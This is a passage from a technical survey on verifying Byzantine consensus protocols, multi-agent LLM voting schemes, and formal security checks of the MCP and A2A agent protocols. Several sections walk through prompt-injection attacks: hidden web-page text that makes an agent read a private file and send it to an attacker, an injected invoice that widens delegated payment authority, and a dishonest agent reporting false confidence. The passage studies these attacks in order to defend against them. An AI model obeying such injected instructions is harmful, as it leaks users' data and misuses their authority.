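The difference between "may" and "must" accounts for everything the liars can do. If no honest replica starts with the value, b is 0, so no honest replica may repeat the value and b stays 0. The liars therefore cannot make anyone accept a value that only they have sent, whatever n and f are.

For larger protocols, a model checker does this automatically. It treats n and f as unknown numbers with n > 3f. Counts such as b never decrease, so each comparison can change from false to true only once, and these changes can happen in only finitely many orders. For each order, the model checker uses an arithmetic solver to check whether any values of n, f and the counts lead to a violation.

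*Formal Verification of Blockchain Byzantine Fault Tolerance* (2019) applies this method to the Red Belly Blockchain. Its broadcast takes 116 lines to describe and 40 seconds to verify, and its consensus algorithm takes 276 lines and 17 minutes on a 64-core machine. *Holistic Verification of Blockchain Consensus* (2022) speeds up verification by checking the broadcast first, then replacing it in the consensus algorithm with its proved properties. Verifying safety and liveness for any n and any f < n/3 this way takes about 70 seconds.

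Part of the Red Belly argument is not machine-checked. Leung, Zeldovich and Kaashoek (2025) point out in *Shipwright* that the Red Belly work states its main property as a complicated formula and relates it to a simpler one only by an informal argument. Another informal argument connects the assumptions about network timing to those the checker uses. The proof covers the algorithm but not the code.

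In the verification tool Ivy, a user can replace the numbers n and f with an axiom that any two quorums have an honest replica in common. The user also proposes an invariant, and Ivy checks whether every step preserves it. These checks are fully automatic if the model stays within a decidable part of first-order logic, which restricts how statements combine "for every" and "there is". In particular, the user has to avoid loops between axioms. The quorum axiom implies that a replica exists for every two quorums. If another axiom implied that a new quorum exists for every replica, the solver might go on producing replicas and quorums forever.

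A proof of this kind holds for any system that satisfies the axiom, even if its quorums are not defined by size. In the Stellar payment network, for example, each participant chooses whom to trust. Bondarev, Ziborov and Yanovich (2026), in *Systematization of Knowledge*, report that Giuliano Losa and Mike Dodds used Ivy to prove Stellar's safety and some liveness properties for arbitrary fixed quorums. They used Isabelle/HOL to justify the model they gave to Ivy. Other researchers have used Ivy to prove the safety of a simplified form of HotStuff, a later Byzantine protocol. This proof was harder than one for a protocol with separate views because HotStuff's replicas build a tree of proposals.

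### Lamport's proof, and proofs about code

In *Byzantizing Paxos by Refinement* (2011), Leslie Lamport constructed a Byzantine version of Paxos that generalises the core of PBFT. Paxos is his earlier consensus protocol for machines that may crash but never send false messages, and it needs 2f + 1 of them to tolerate f crashes. Lamport saw PBFT as a way for 2f + 1 honest machines to run Paxos among f malicious ones without knowing which are malicious. He proved that his Byzantine version refines the original, meaning that everything the honest machines do corresponds to something ordinary Paxos allows. The honest machines therefore inherit the safety of Paxos.

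TLAPS, a proof checker for Lamport's specification language TLA+, verified the safety part of this argument. *Mechanically Checked Safety Proof of a Byzantine Paxos Algorithm* reports that the proof assumes a few simple facts about finite sets, such as that a non-empty finite set of integers has a largest element. Lamport did not write a formal liveness property for the Byzantine algorithm. A model checker was of limited use because it could not handle instances large enough to give him any confidence in the algorithm.

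In 2018, Vincent Rahli and colleagues used Velisarios, their framework for the proof assistant Coq (now called Rocq), to produce the first machine-checked safety proof for an implementation of PBFT. The proof shows that honest replicas never disagree, but it does not establish liveness, the guarantee that they eventually finish. This is typical of the more than 20 verified protocols that Bondarev and colleagues surveyed. They explain that liveness is harder to prove because it depends on timeouts, message delivery and sometimes randomness, as well as on the protocol itself.

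Leung and colleagues proved safety and liveness for an executable version of PBFT. They wrote it in Dafny, a language in which programmers write code and proofs together, and then translated it into Go. To avoid reasoning about infinite runs, they gave each task a measure of how close it is to completion and proved statements about pairs of states. The PBFT part has 31,138 lines, mostly proofs and internal specifications, and a reader has to trust 266 of them. The framework adds 13,357 lines, of which 1,351 are trusted.

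The liveness proof exposed a bug in their own code. The bug appeared when the network dropped all commit messages, then dropped the prepare messages of the next view, and then recovered completely. The honest replicas signed view-change messages, and an honest new primary included these in its announcement. But the code re-encoded the messages incorrectly, so the replicas rejected signatures they had just made, and this happened again in every later view. No replica ever accepted a wrong result, so a safety proof would not have revealed the problem. A tester would have had to produce that sequence of network failures to find it.

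The prototype is still far from a complete service. It agrees on only one log entry, and inefficient generated code slows it down. The proof also assumes that the networking and cryptographic software is correct. Unverified code can be much worse. In *Beyond the Whitepaper*, Wong, Kolegov and Mikushin (2024) draw on their security audits to describe logic errors, concurrency bugs and cryptographic vulnerabilities in implementations of Byzantine protocols.

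### Proofs written by language models

Formal proofs of consensus protocols have often taken several person-months each, according to *The End of Consensus Research?* (Burgelin, Guerraoui and colleagues, 2026). Language models have made them much cheaper. Burgelin and colleagues had an agent based on GPT-6.1 Sol design a consensus protocol, implement it and prove it safe in the proof assistant Lean. This took about 24 hours and cost an estimated $199. The proof and the formal model it refers to total about 98,000 lines and accounted for 91% of the text the language model processed.

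The protocol tolerates crashes but not Byzantine faults, and the proof covers safety but not liveness. People also had to correct the design, because the agent had copied a flaw from a published protocol and had exploited the simulated network. It sent duplicate messages over two connections and used whichever arrived first, which is unlikely to help on a real network. While formalising existing protocols as examples, the agent found four previously unreported safety flaws in two of them, EPaxos Revisited and Bodega.

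*Dugong* (Danezis, Kokoris-Kogias and Sonnino, 2026) contains the most extensive Byzantine proof of this kind. It covers a family of protocols that several blockchains use. In every round, each replica publishes a block of transactions that refers to blocks from the previous round. These references count as votes, so replicas do not send votes separately. Danezis and colleagues wrote one general algorithm with adjustable thresholds. Different settings reproduce eight published protocols and yield four new ones, some of which tolerate a mixture of replicas that crash and replicas that send false messages.

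Much of the safety proof rests on a more general form of the quorum argument. If two groups of replicas have more than n + f members in total, they share at least one that is not Byzantine. PBFT's quorums only just meet this condition, since they have 4f + 2 members in total and n + f is 4f + 1. The same rule shows what it costs to save a round of messages:

1. The leader of a round proposes a block, and a replica commits it after n − f votes, without a further round to confirm them.
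2. Another replica may have missed some of these votes. It relies on a later block, which refers to blocks from n − f replicas. These two groups of n − f overlap in at least n − 2f replicas, of which f may have told it something different. It can therefore count on seeing only n − 3f of the votes, and has to commit on that number.
3. If the leader equivocated, a conflicting block must never get n − 3f votes. The rule excludes this if (n − f) + (n − 3f) > n + f, which means n > 5f.

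Committing in two rounds requires at least 5f + 1 replicas, while committing in three requires only 3f + 1. Danezis and colleagues reduced the safety of each type of protocol to three inequalities on its thresholds and proved that satisfying them is sufficient. A designer who changes the thresholds only has to check the inequalities again.

The proofs cover both safety and liveness and take up about 125,000 lines of Lean. AI agents wrote most of them, while people reviewed the definitions and theorem statements. The work also uncovered a missing tie-breaking rule in one published protocol and attacks on two others, Black Marlin and S-Minnow. The attacks resemble the one on Zyzzyva and, like it, need only four replicas, one of them Byzantine. Each protocol has one rule for committing a block directly and another for settling it later, and an equivocating leader can make the two rules choose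 different blocks. Black Marlin appeared in 2025 and S-Minnow in 2026, so their flaws were found much sooner after publication than Zyzzyva's.

| Proof | What it establishes | Size or time | Main gaps |
|---|---|---|---|
| *Holistic Verification of Blockchain Consensus* | safety and liveness of Red Belly's consensus | about 70 seconds of computation | code; link to network timing |
| Leung and colleagues | safety and liveness of executable PBFT code | 31,138 lines, plus a framework of 13,357 | more than one log entry; networking and cryptographic code |
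| Burgelin and colleagues | safety of a new crash-tolerant protocol | 98,000 lines; about 24 hours, including the design | liveness; code |
| Danezis and colleagues | safety and liveness of twelve related protocols | 125,000 lines | production code |

When Lean has checked a proof, people only need to read what it proves. A theorem about every run that meets certain conditions is true but useless if no run can meet them. *Barnacle* (2026), which verifies a method for choosing leaders in the same family of protocols, guards against this with about 3,200 lines of concrete examples that test every definition. A reader still has to check about 1,900 lines of definitions and theorem statements, but can skip the roughly 2,000 lines of AI-generated proofs. *Dugong* also includes about 40,000 lines of concrete examples.

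Most of this work still doesn't link its proofs to running software. Danezis and colleagues proved that a Lean version of their algorithm meets its specification, but the library meant for actual use is about 25,000 lines of Rust with no formal connection to the proof. They ran the library in about 3,000 simulations and never saw two honest replicas commit conflicting results. The simulations included replicas that crashed or equivocated in a set pattern, but not the arbitrary Byzantine behavior that the proof covers.

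## Groups of language-model agents with some members assumed faulty

Proofs about Byzantine agreement assume that at most f of the n members are faulty. A designer has to argue separately that no single cause, such as a bug, a stolen password or a misleading document, will corrupt more than f members. This is why Castro and Liskov wanted PBFT's replicas to differ from one another. The argument is harder to make for language models, which may have learned from much the same text and often read the same inputs.

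Suppose four agents answer a question together, using a protocol that tolerates one faulty agent, and each agent fails with probability 0.05. If they fail independently, the probability that none fails is 0.95<sup>4</sup>, about 0.815, and the probability that exactly one fails is 4 × 0.05 × 0.95<sup>3</sup>, about 0.171. That leaves about 0.014 for two or more failures, which the protocol does not tolerate. If there is also a shared cause that occurs with probability 0.02 and makes all four fail, the probability of two or more failures rises to 0.02 + 0.98 × 0.014, or about 0.034.

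Larger groups help much less when there is a shared cause:

| Agents | Failures tolerated | Probability of too many, independent failures only | With the shared cause added |
|---|---|---|---|
| 4 | 1 | 0.014 | 0.034 |
| 7 | 2 | 0.004 | 0.024 |
| 10 | 3 | 0.001 | 0.021 |

The last column can never fall below 0.02, however many agents the designer adds.

Agents are most likely to fail together when they are copies of one model reading the same poisoned document. Suppose the email assistant's developer has four copies of the model vote on every outgoing mail, and all four read the stranger's fake invoice. An injected instruction that works on one copy will probably work on the others, so a single message could make all four agents faulty.

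### Separately written programs that fail together

Engineers tested the independence assumption long before language models existed. In N-version programming, several people write the same program from one specification, and a voter compares the versions' outputs. For *An Experimental Evaluation of the Assumption of Independence in Multi-Version Programming* (1986), Knight and Leveson collected 27 versions from programmers at two universities and ran them on one million tests. The individual programs were extremely reliable, but more than one failed on the same test substantially more often than they would have if their failures were independent.

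The programmers had not communicated with each other, but *N-Version Programming with Coding Agents* (2026) explains that people with similar training or reference materials tend to misinterpret a specification in the same way. *A Systematic Methodology for Evaluating Failure Independence in LLM-Generated Code* (2026), which proposes a similar test for programs written by language models, also attributes such shared errors to common design strategies.

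Some proponents of N-version programming criticized the experiment. In *A Reply to the Criticisms of the Knight & Leveson Experiment*, Knight and Leveson accused them of making inaccurate statements about it. Knight and Leveson had limited their conclusion to the problem their programmers solved, but Les Hatton's partial replication with a different task did not find independent failures either. Hatton later showed that several versions can be usefully more reliable than one even if their failures are correlated.

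Butler and Finelli, in *The Infeasibility of Experimental Quantification of Life-Critical Software Reliability*, argue that experiments cannot justify the independence assumption for software that must be extremely reliable. Joint failures would have to be so rare that no feasible amount of testing could measure their rate.

### How often language models make the same mistake

Kim, Garg and colleagues compared the answers of 71 models to 14,042 multiple-choice questions in *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025). When two models were both wrong, they chose the same wrong answer 60% of the time on average. If they had chosen at random among the three wrong options, they would have agreed about 33% of the time. Models from the same company agreed more often, and so did more accurate models, even after the researchers controlled for company. A model from Google and one from the company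 Writer gave the same answer to 99.9% of the questions that both got wrong, although Kim and colleagues knew of no publicly stated connection between them. Using models from different companies therefore doesn't guarantee that their errors will be independent.

In *Nine Judges, Two Effective Votes*, Kohli (2026) asked nine models from seven families whether one sentence follows from another, contradicts it or does neither. Kohli took the majority opinion of 100 people as the correct answer. A majority vote of the models was right on 72.0% of 1,000 sentence pairs. If the models had erred independently on pairs of the same difficulty, the vote would have been right on about 94%. All nine models were wrong on 51 pairs; if their errors had been independent, the expected number would have been less than one.

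Kohli expresses the loss as an effective number of votes:

n<sub>eff</sub> = k / (1 + (k − 1)φ)

Here k is the number of models and φ is the average correlation between the errors of two models. With k = 9 and φ = 0.391, the result is about 2.2. As k grows, the formula approaches 1/φ, or about 2.6, so adding more models of the same kind would hardly help. However, Kohli deliberately included many pairs on which people disagree, so an answer counted as wrong was sometimes just a minority opinion.

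In *Do Large Language Models Know Colombian Law?* (2026), models that got a question wrong chose the same wrong option 87% of the time. At least one of 15 models was right on 98.4% of the questions, but a majority vote was right on only 84.3%. In most of these tests, the best single model did better than the vote:

| Test | Models | Majority vote | Best single model |
|---|---|---|---|
| Kohli, sentence pairs from MNLI | 9 | 72.0% | 71.8% |
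| Kohli, sentence pairs from SNLI | 9 | 77.7% | 84.2% |
| Kohli, choosing the likelier explanation | 9 | 88.7% | 91.2% |
| *Do Large Language Models Know Colombian Law?* | 15 | 84.3% | 90.5% |

The comparison slightly favours the single model, because a user without the answer key would not know which model is best.

Correlations between pairs of models can also understate how often the whole group fails. Suppose three models each get half of the questions wrong, and the first two fail independently. If the third fails exactly when the other two are both right or both wrong, all three fail together on a quarter of the questions. If it fails exactly when only one of the other two is wrong, all three never fail together. In both cases, any two of the models fail independently, so the correlation between them is zero.

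Chen (2026), in *When Does Combining Language Models Help?*, found such a gap in a test of 67 models from 21 providers. All of them failed on 17 of 330 mathematics questions (5.2%), although the pairwise correlations predicted only 2.3%. A vote that picks one of the models' answers could therefore have scored at most 94.8%. Seventeen questions is a small sample, though, and an error in the answer key would also look like a failure of every model.

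These correlations make it less likely that at most f members are faulty, as the quorum argument assumes, but the argument itself remains valid. *Semantic Quorum Assurance* (2026) proposes choosing the members of each quorum according to how often their errors have coincided, and requiring a mixture of models. That should help with ordinary mistakes, but past mistakes are a poor guide to whether an attacker can find one input that fools every model in the group.

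### Six faulty agents out of seven

Some experiments nevertheless report success with far more than a third of the agents faulty. Zheng, Chen and colleagues (2025), in *Rethinking the Reliability of Multi-agent System*, report it with six faulty agents out of seven, a fault rate of 85.7%. Their method, CP-WBFT, relies on confidence:

1. Each agent answers the question and attaches a confidence between 0 and 1.
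2. An agent adopts a neighbour's answer if the neighbour is more confident.
3. The group chooses the answer whose supporters have the highest average confidence. The number of supporters only breaks ties.

The researchers either asked the model for its confidence or estimated it by training a small classifier to predict from the model's internal activations whether the model's answer was right.

Their main tests used ten grade-school mathematics questions and ten questions about safety. They chose questions that a stronger model tends to get right and a weaker one tends to get wrong. One copy of the stronger model then served as the honest agent, and six copies of the weaker one served as the "Byzantine" agents. These are the results when every agent could communicate with every other:

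| Source of confidence | Honest and "Byzantine" models | Questions | Agents' accuracy before | Agents' accuracy after | Group's accuracy |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| the model's own statement | GPT-4o-mini, GPT-3.5-turbo | mathematics | 70% | 90% | 90% |
| the model's own statement | GPT-4o-mini, GPT-3.5-turbo | safety | 26% | 30% | 30% |
| internal activations | Llama 3.1 8B, Llama 3 8B | mathematics | 14% | 100% | 100% |
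| internal activations | Llama 3.1 8B, Llama 3 8B | safety | 14% | 100% | 100% |

The setup makes the perfect scores less surprising. An accuracy of 14% is one agent in seven, as one would expect if only the stronger model was right. The method then had to recognise that model as the most reliable, on questions selected to make the difference between the models large. In the first row, the agents started at 70%, so the six "Byzantine" agents must have been right at least 65% of the time on average.

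The classical limit of one third, which Zheng and colleagues present their results as exceeding, applies to a different problem. In the generals' problem, only the commander knows the order, so a lieutenant has to rely on what others tell him. In Zheng and colleagues' setting, every agent receives the question and can work out the answer alone, so an agent that ignored all its neighbours would be unaffected no matter how many of them were faulty.

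The condition for success also differs. Byzantine agreement requires all the honest members to reach the same decision in every run. If only one member is honest, it has no other honest member to disagree with. Zheng and colleagues instead measured how often the answers were correct, averaged over ten questions.

The attackers in these tests were also mild. They were weaker models that followed the protocol, sent all their neighbours the same answer and did not misreport their confidence. Success against them does not contradict the classical theorem. Under that theorem, when n ≤ 3f, every protocol for unsigned messages fails against some behaviour by the traitors, but not necessarily against every behaviour. Even the classical results allow more than a third of the members to be faulty under other assumptions, such as signed orders that arrive on time.

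*The Six Sigma Agent* (2026) uses a different threshold. It treats a model's errors as crashes and uses 2f + 1 agents to tolerate f faulty ones. But a mistaken model still casts a vote, unlike a crashed machine, which sends nothing. Majority voting among 2f + 1 agents can still work if one trusted program collects the answers, because no agent can then send different answers to different members. The f + 1 correct agents must also give the same answer, and correlated errors must not affect more than f agents.

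### One agent that claims to be certain

Lee, Yun and colleagues (2026) object in *Robust Multi-Agent LLMs under Byzantine Faults* that CP-WBFT assumes faulty agents report their confidence honestly. A Byzantine agent can report a confidence of 1.0 in a wrong answer. Every less confident neighbour then adopts that answer, and no other answer can have a higher average confidence. Reading the confidence from internal activations would not solve this if the faulty agent controls the software that takes the reading.

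Their alternative, Self-Anchored Consensus (SAC), ignores what agents report about themselves. In each round, an agent does the following:

1. It sends its current answer to its neighbours.
2. It uses its own model to score every answer it receives, as well as its own answer.
3. It discards up to F of the lowest-scoring answers, but only those that score below its own.
4. It gives the remaining answers and their scores to its model, which revises the answer or keeps it.

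F is the largest number of faulty neighbours that the design allows for. If the network has enough connections, every agent keeps at least one neighbour's answer after discarding others. Every answer that a reliable agent keeps scores at least as high as the lowest-scoring answer from any reliable agent. The score comes from the agent's own model, so this guarantee depends on how well the model judges answers. With seven agents and six rounds, each question takes 91 model calls, compared with seven if each agent answers once.

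Lee and colleagues tested both methods with seven agents. Most tests had four strong agents, two weaker ones and one adversary, which submitted answers from a weak model with a confidence of 1.0. The last test had three adversaries and no weaker agents. The table gives the accuracy of the strong agents before and after the discussion, with every agent connected to every other:

| Test | Strong model | CP-WBFT | SAC |
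|---|---|---|---|
| 100 MATH problems | GPT-4o-mini | 81% to 50% | 81% to 78% |
| 30 commonsense questions | GPT-5 | 85% to 17% | 83% to 82% |
| MATH-500 | Qwen3-4B | 68% to 47% | 68% to 72% |
| AIME 2025 competition | Qwen3-4B-Thinking | 78% to 0% | 74% to 67% |
| HMMT-25 competition | GPT-5.6 Sol | 100% to 10% | 100% to 93% |

The results support the objection to self-reported confidence. In the AIME test, a single dishonest agent reduced every agent's accuracy to zero. SAC prevented most of this damage, but in four of the five tests the strong agents would have done slightly better working alone. SAC helped the weaker agents in every test that included them.

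These tests cover only one kind of attack. In SAC, every honest model must read the adversary's text to score it, and that text could contain an injected instruction to award full marks. Lee and colleagues did not test this. They acknowledge another weakness, that an overconfident agent may give correct answers low scores and keep its own wrong one.

### Combining the judges' scores

*Byzantine-Robust Decentralized Coordination of LLM Agents* (Jo and Park, 2025) describes DecentLLMs, a system in which several worker agents answer the user's question independently. Separate evaluator agents then give each answer up to 20 points on each of five criteria, such as logical consistency. The system combines the evaluators' scores for an answer by taking their geometric median, the point with the smallest total distance to all the scores. A few extreme scores move this point much less than they would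 move an average. The system then selects the answer with the highest combined score.

The system assumes signed messages, a known limit on delays and an honest majority in both groups. It answered 71 of 100 MMLU-Pro benchmark questions correctly. Jo and Park compare this with 64 for a vote that needs two thirds of the agents and 50 for a simple majority. They did not run full versions of those two systems, but assumed that the leader would propose a fairly low-ranked answer that could still collect enough votes.

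Jo and Park tested resistance to attack on one question, with eight honest evaluators and a worker whose answer contained advertisements and altered numbers. They then added dishonest evaluators, who gave that answer full marks and every other answer zero. The system chose a correct answer with up to six dishonest evaluators and the attacker's answer with seven. Eight of the 15 evaluators were honest in that last case, so a bare honest majority was not enough. Jo and Park's formal requirement is slightly stricter than a bare majority and allows only six dishonest evaluators.

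Honest evaluators often disagreed. They gave one correct answer total scores from 19 to 100, and its combined score was 55.6. A wrong answer from an honest worker received 83.0. Jo and Park call the reliability of the scores an important problem for future work.

### Agreeing and being right

Agreement does not make a decision correct, as in the example of the faulty radar, yet most of the experiments above measure correctness. In Kohli's main test, the nine models were unanimous on 319 sentence pairs and right on 290 of them, or 90.9%. Nine independent voters of the same accuracy would be right almost every time they all agreed. Correct replicas would still have accepted the 29 wrong answers without any fault in the protocol.

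In *Can AI Agents Agree?* (2026), groups of agents based on Qwen3-8B or Qwen3-14B exchange proposals and try to settle on a number. No number is better than another, so the task tests only agreement, and every message arrives on time. A single Byzantine agent was enough to make the rate of successful agreement collapse. Most failures were failures of liveness, meaning that the group did not reach a decision, and the adversary rarely got the group to accept a corrupted value.

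The generals' procedure solves this kind of problem with one traitor among four. However, the loyal generals follow the procedure exactly, whereas these agents decide what to do next by interpreting a text. A designer can avoid this difficulty by having the models propose values and having ordinary code exchange the messages and count the votes.

The code also needs a way to decide whether two answers match. *Certifiable Semantic Agreement Among LLM Agents* (2026) points out that classical protocols require matching values to be identical byte for byte, which language models' answers are not. Two honest agents may write "£1,000" and "one thousand pounds", and a program that compares bytes would count these as different votes. Multiple-choice questions and numerical answers avoid this problem, but most emails and computer programs do not. If another model judges whether two answers mean the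 same, the result also depends on that model.

### Whether the classical results still apply

In *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents*, Chu (2026) calls the classical guarantees "inapplicable" to networks of language-model agents. Chu argues that these guarantees assume deterministic, verifiable behaviour and a fixed, known number of faulty members, whereas language models behave randomly and may turn faulty gradually. Chu also states that Jo and Park proved such agents need new verification methods.

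Jo and Park's paper contains no such proof. It presents and tests a system that uses a classical protocol to ensure that all honest evaluators receive the same messages. The survey's bibliography lists this paper twice, with different authors.

Chu cites Lamport and colleagues and Castro and Liskov for the classical assumptions, but neither paper requires faulty members to be deterministic or verifiable. Like the traitors in the Byzantine generals problem, a faulty member may act at random or start misbehaving late, and f is only an upper limit on the number of faulty members. PBFT, Castro and Liskov's protocol, does require the replicated service to be deterministic, and a language model that generates a new answer on every replica does not meet that condition.

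Chu has a stronger argument that the number of compromised agents can grow. The survey describes an experiment in which an adversarial image injected into one agent spread to others through their ordinary messages. If such an attack can reach more than f agents, the guarantee no longer holds, because the theorem's conditions are not met. A designer who can meet those conditions still gets the guarantee. The impossibility results also still hold, because they require only that a faulty member can imitate honest ones.

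### LogAct: a shared log without a fault bound

Balakrishnan, Bharambe and colleagues (2026), in *LogAct*, decline to assume any limit on the number of faulty agents. They consider such an assumption unreasonable for agents working on live systems, and running 3f + 1 copies of an agent too expensive. They do keep another part of replicated services, the shared log, which is a permanent record that programs can add to but not rewrite. In LogAct, an agent's action has to appear in the log before it happens:

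1. The driver sends the conversation to the language model and records the action that the model proposes.
2. One or more voters read the proposal and record their votes. A voter may be a set of fixed rules or another language model.
3. The decider applies a fixed policy to the votes and records either a commit or an abort.
4. The executor carries out committed actions and records the results.

PBFT's replicas vote on the order of requests, whereas LogAct's voters decide whether an action may happen. Each LogAct component can add only certain types of entry to the log, so the executor, which runs code written by the model, cannot cast a vote.

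The log also lets a driver recover from a restart despite the model's randomness. It contains everything the model produced, so the driver can replay those outputs and reach the same state without calling the model again. Voters and the decider also recover their state from the log. The email assistant could use such a log to restore its flag after a crash.

Replaying the executor's actions would be unsafe because it might send the same mail twice, so a restarted executor only records that it has restarted. The model then proposes ways to find out what has already happened, and the voters vote on these proposals as they do on any others. In one test, Balakrishnan and colleagues stopped an agent that was working too slowly, after it had processed 1,184 of 2,000 folders. Its replacement read the log, found a faster method and processed only the remaining 816.

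Balakrishnan and colleagues assume nothing about the user's request, the model's output or the data it reads. They distinguish three results of a harmful action that the voters wrongly approve:

- The action damages the outside system, for example by deleting data. The log still records what happened.
- The action alters the executor, which may then report false results, so the log no longer matches reality.
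- The action alters the voters or the decider, which may then approve anything. LogAct prevents this by running them separately from the executor, under different identities.

Voters also have to allow for changes between the vote and the action. If a voter approves a withdrawal because the account has enough money, the withdrawal may still fail or overdraw the account, because another program may empty it before the withdrawal runs. The voter should instead check that the action tests the balance as it withdraws the money.

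The researchers tested LogAct on AgentDojo, a benchmark of prompt-injection attacks on agents that use tools. They used a model from 2024 that is easy to attack:

| Voters | Attacks that succeeded | Ordinary tasks completed | Average time |
|---|---|---|---|
| none | 48.2% | 81.4% | 6.7 seconds |
| fixed rules | 1.4% | 49.5% | 10.6 seconds |
| fixed rules or a language model | 1.4% | 78.4% | 12.2 seconds |

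The remaining attacks changed only the agent's reply to the user, so there was no action to vote on. A language model wrote the rules after examining the agent's behaviour on this benchmark, so these figures probably overstate how well the rules would stop unfamiliar attacks.

The last row also has a weaker guarantee. Rules alone can guarantee, for example, that no mail goes to an unapproved address. With two voters, the policy was to carry out an action if either approved it. The second voter was the same model as the agent, and it read tool results that might contain injected instructions. An attack that got its approval could therefore override the rules, although none did in this test. Requiring both voters to approve would preserve the guarantee, but the agent could then complete no more tasks than the rules alone allow.

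## MCP and A2A: protocol verification applied to agents

A LogAct agent keeps its log, voters and executor inside one system. Many agents also use shared protocols to reach software that other people run. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) connects language models to tools. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) specifies that a server lists its tools with their names, descriptions and expected inputs. The model picks one, the scaffold sends the call, and the result goes back to the model. Agent2Agent (A2A) lets one agent give a task to another. Each agent publishes a card describing its abilities, and the two exchange messages and results. The email assistant could get its three tools from MCP servers and use A2A to have a bookkeeping agent process an invoice.

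Encryption protects these messages on the network, but a genuine server can still return text that contains an injected instruction. Zheng, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Security Analysis of Agent Protocol Composition*, take an example from the security research group Snyk Labs:

1. A user asks an agent to summarise a web page, which the agent fetches through one MCP server.
2. Hidden text on the page tells the model to read a private file, which it does through a second server.
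3. The model sends the contents to the attacker through the first server.

Every message is well formed, and each server does what it should. Checking either server alone would miss the attack.

### A network attacker with three more actions

Zheng, Zhang and colleagues built AgentThread, which checks the specifications of five agent protocols using TLC, a model checker for Lamport's language TLA+. It then tries some of the attacks it finds on real software. AgentThread is the successor to AgentRFC, a framework from March 2026. *InterSAGE* (2026), which proposes a secure agent protocol, credits AgentRFC with stating eleven security principles as TLA+ invariants. It also credits AgentRFC with the principle of composition safety, which is that protocols that are secure separately may be insecure together.

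The attacker in AgentThread has the powers of the Dolev-Yao attacker and three more:

- *inject*: put instructions into a tool's output, a web page or a message from another agent;
- *inflate*: claim capabilities that a tool or agent does not have;
- *amplify*: gain authority through delegation or a chain of tools.

AgentThread takes the security of the connections for granted, so the three new actions matter most.

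The model also labels each step by its cause. Protocol steps are those that a specification permits, such as delegating a task. Environment steps happen without malice, such as the expiry of an access token. Adversary steps use the attacker's powers. The labels show whether a failure needs an attacker. In MCP, for example, TLC found a trace with no adversary steps in which a session opens and closes but the credential it used stays valid.

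### Reading the delegation check

One of AgentThread's checks requires that delegation never give an agent more authority than its original grant. A simplified version in TLA+ could look like this:

```
DelegationWithinGrant ==
  \A a \in Agents :
    \A c \in Capabilities :
      (c \in held[a]) => (c \in granted[a])
```

- The first line names the invariant.
- The second line makes it cover every agent a.
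- The third line makes it cover every capability c, such as reading invoices.
- The last line states that if a now holds c, then c was part of a's original grant.

Suppose the email assistant lets the bookkeeping agent read invoices. An adversary step then delegates that permission again, widened to include paying them. The bookkeeping agent now holds a capability outside its grant, so the last line is false. TLC found such a trace for A2A, whose specification sets no limits on delegation.

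A reader could find the missing limit in the specification without a model checker. Zheng and colleagues reply that reading the text does not show whether the bad state is reachable or provide a trace to try on real software. The point about reachability is rather weak for the delegation check, because the model gives the attacker the action that the specification does not restrict.

To build the models, a partly automated process extracts requirements from each specification and records whether each is mandatory, recommended or absent. AgentThread found 37 relevant clauses for MCP and 17 for A2A. If a clause has two possible readings, the model allows both. Automatic checks reject a record if its source passage does not exist, but people still choose the documents and write the code that connects the model to each piece of software.

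### Results for the separate protocols

Zheng and colleagues applied eleven checks to each of five protocols: MCP; A2A; the Agent Network Protocol (ANP), which verifies agents' identities; the Agent Communication Protocol (ACP); and the Agent Client Protocol for coding agents. Of the 55 combinations of protocol and check, 35 failed, 10 passed and 10 did not apply or went unchecked. No protocol passed every check that applied to it.

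They count 12 of the 35 failures as confirmed by tests on software. This figure is uncertain because their test summary also lists several ANP and Agent Client Protocol failures as reproduced, and these are not among the 12. They ran 80 tests, compared with 42 for AgentRFC, but some of the 80 only inspected source code to confirm that a control was missing.

The clearest violation concerns MCP, whose specification requires servers to sanitize tool outputs. The official software library did not sanitize them, and five test injections passed through unchanged. Three official example servers also passed on every injection the researchers tried. The July 2026 specification keeps the requirement but does not define what a server should remove, and no known filter reliably separates an instruction from ordinary text. The tests show that injected text reaches the model, which may or may not obey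 it.

Most of the other failures break no rule in the specification. AgentThread calls a failure a violation only if the specification makes the control mandatory. It calls the failure a recommendation gap if the specification only recommends the control, and a design gap if the specification doesn't mention it. The 35 failures therefore include many cases where a protocol doesn't meet a standard that Zheng and colleagues chose themselves.

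### An injection that widens a delegation

AgentThread's main combined model connects MCP to A2A through a bridge, the program that carries information from one protocol to the other. The bridge may itself be an agent that coordinates others. The attack goes as follows:

1. An MCP tool returns text with an injected instruction.
2. The bridge accepts the text without sanitizing it, and the model marks the bridge as tainted.
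3. The bridge delegates a task over A2A, and the recipient gains more authority than its original grant.
4. Neither protocol has a complete record of what happened, because the bridge lies outside both of their logs.

In the email assistant's case, text inside an invoice could lead the assistant to give the bookkeeping agent permission to pay it.

A2A had already failed the delegation check on its own, although Zheng and colleagues write that this expansion of authority appears only at the boundary between the protocols. In the combined model, an attacker can also trigger that failure just by influencing a tool's output, without controlling any agent. The researchers did not replay this attack on live software.

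They built eight combined models with 43 security checks, of which 30 failed:

| Combination | Checks | Failures | Example of a failure |
|---|---|---|---|
| MCP and A2A | 9 | 7 | an injection widens a delegation |
| chained MCP servers | 7 | 5 | trust in one server extends to the server behind it |
| MCP and Agent Client Protocol | 6 | 4 | injected text leads to an action on the user's computer |
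| A2A and ACP | 5 | 3 | the protocols define authority differently |
| MCP and ACP | 4 | 3 | a request bypasses the user's consent |
| ANP and MCP | 4 | 3 | a server with a verified identity returns harmful text |
| ANP and A2A | 4 | 3 | an agent with a verified identity exceeds its authority |
| two A2A systems | 4 | 2 | authority grows as it passes between them |

Twelve of the 43 checks are positive controls, which test, for example, that the bridge does not invent credentials. If all twelve held, only one of the other 31, which check for attack paths, also held. Similarly, 20 of AgentRFC's 21 composition checks failed.

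Such failures are hard to fix because nobody is responsible for the bridge. A server's developer can repair that server, but neither protocol has a rule that text from the web must not authorise reading a local file. Across four of the protocols, Zheng and colleagues found only one security control, ANP's identity check, that was both assigned to somebody in a specification and enforced by the software.

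### How far the results reach

TLC explored runs of up to 12 operations. The model of MCP and A2A had two sessions, three agents, three capabilities and eight messages. A check that passes in AgentThread may still fail in a longer run, whereas a ProVerif or Tamarin proof can cover unlimited sessions. These limits matter less for the checks that failed, since a short run is enough to show an attack. Zheng and colleagues argue that more participants would mostly add equivalent orderings of the same events, but they warn against reading their results as proofs for unbounded systems.

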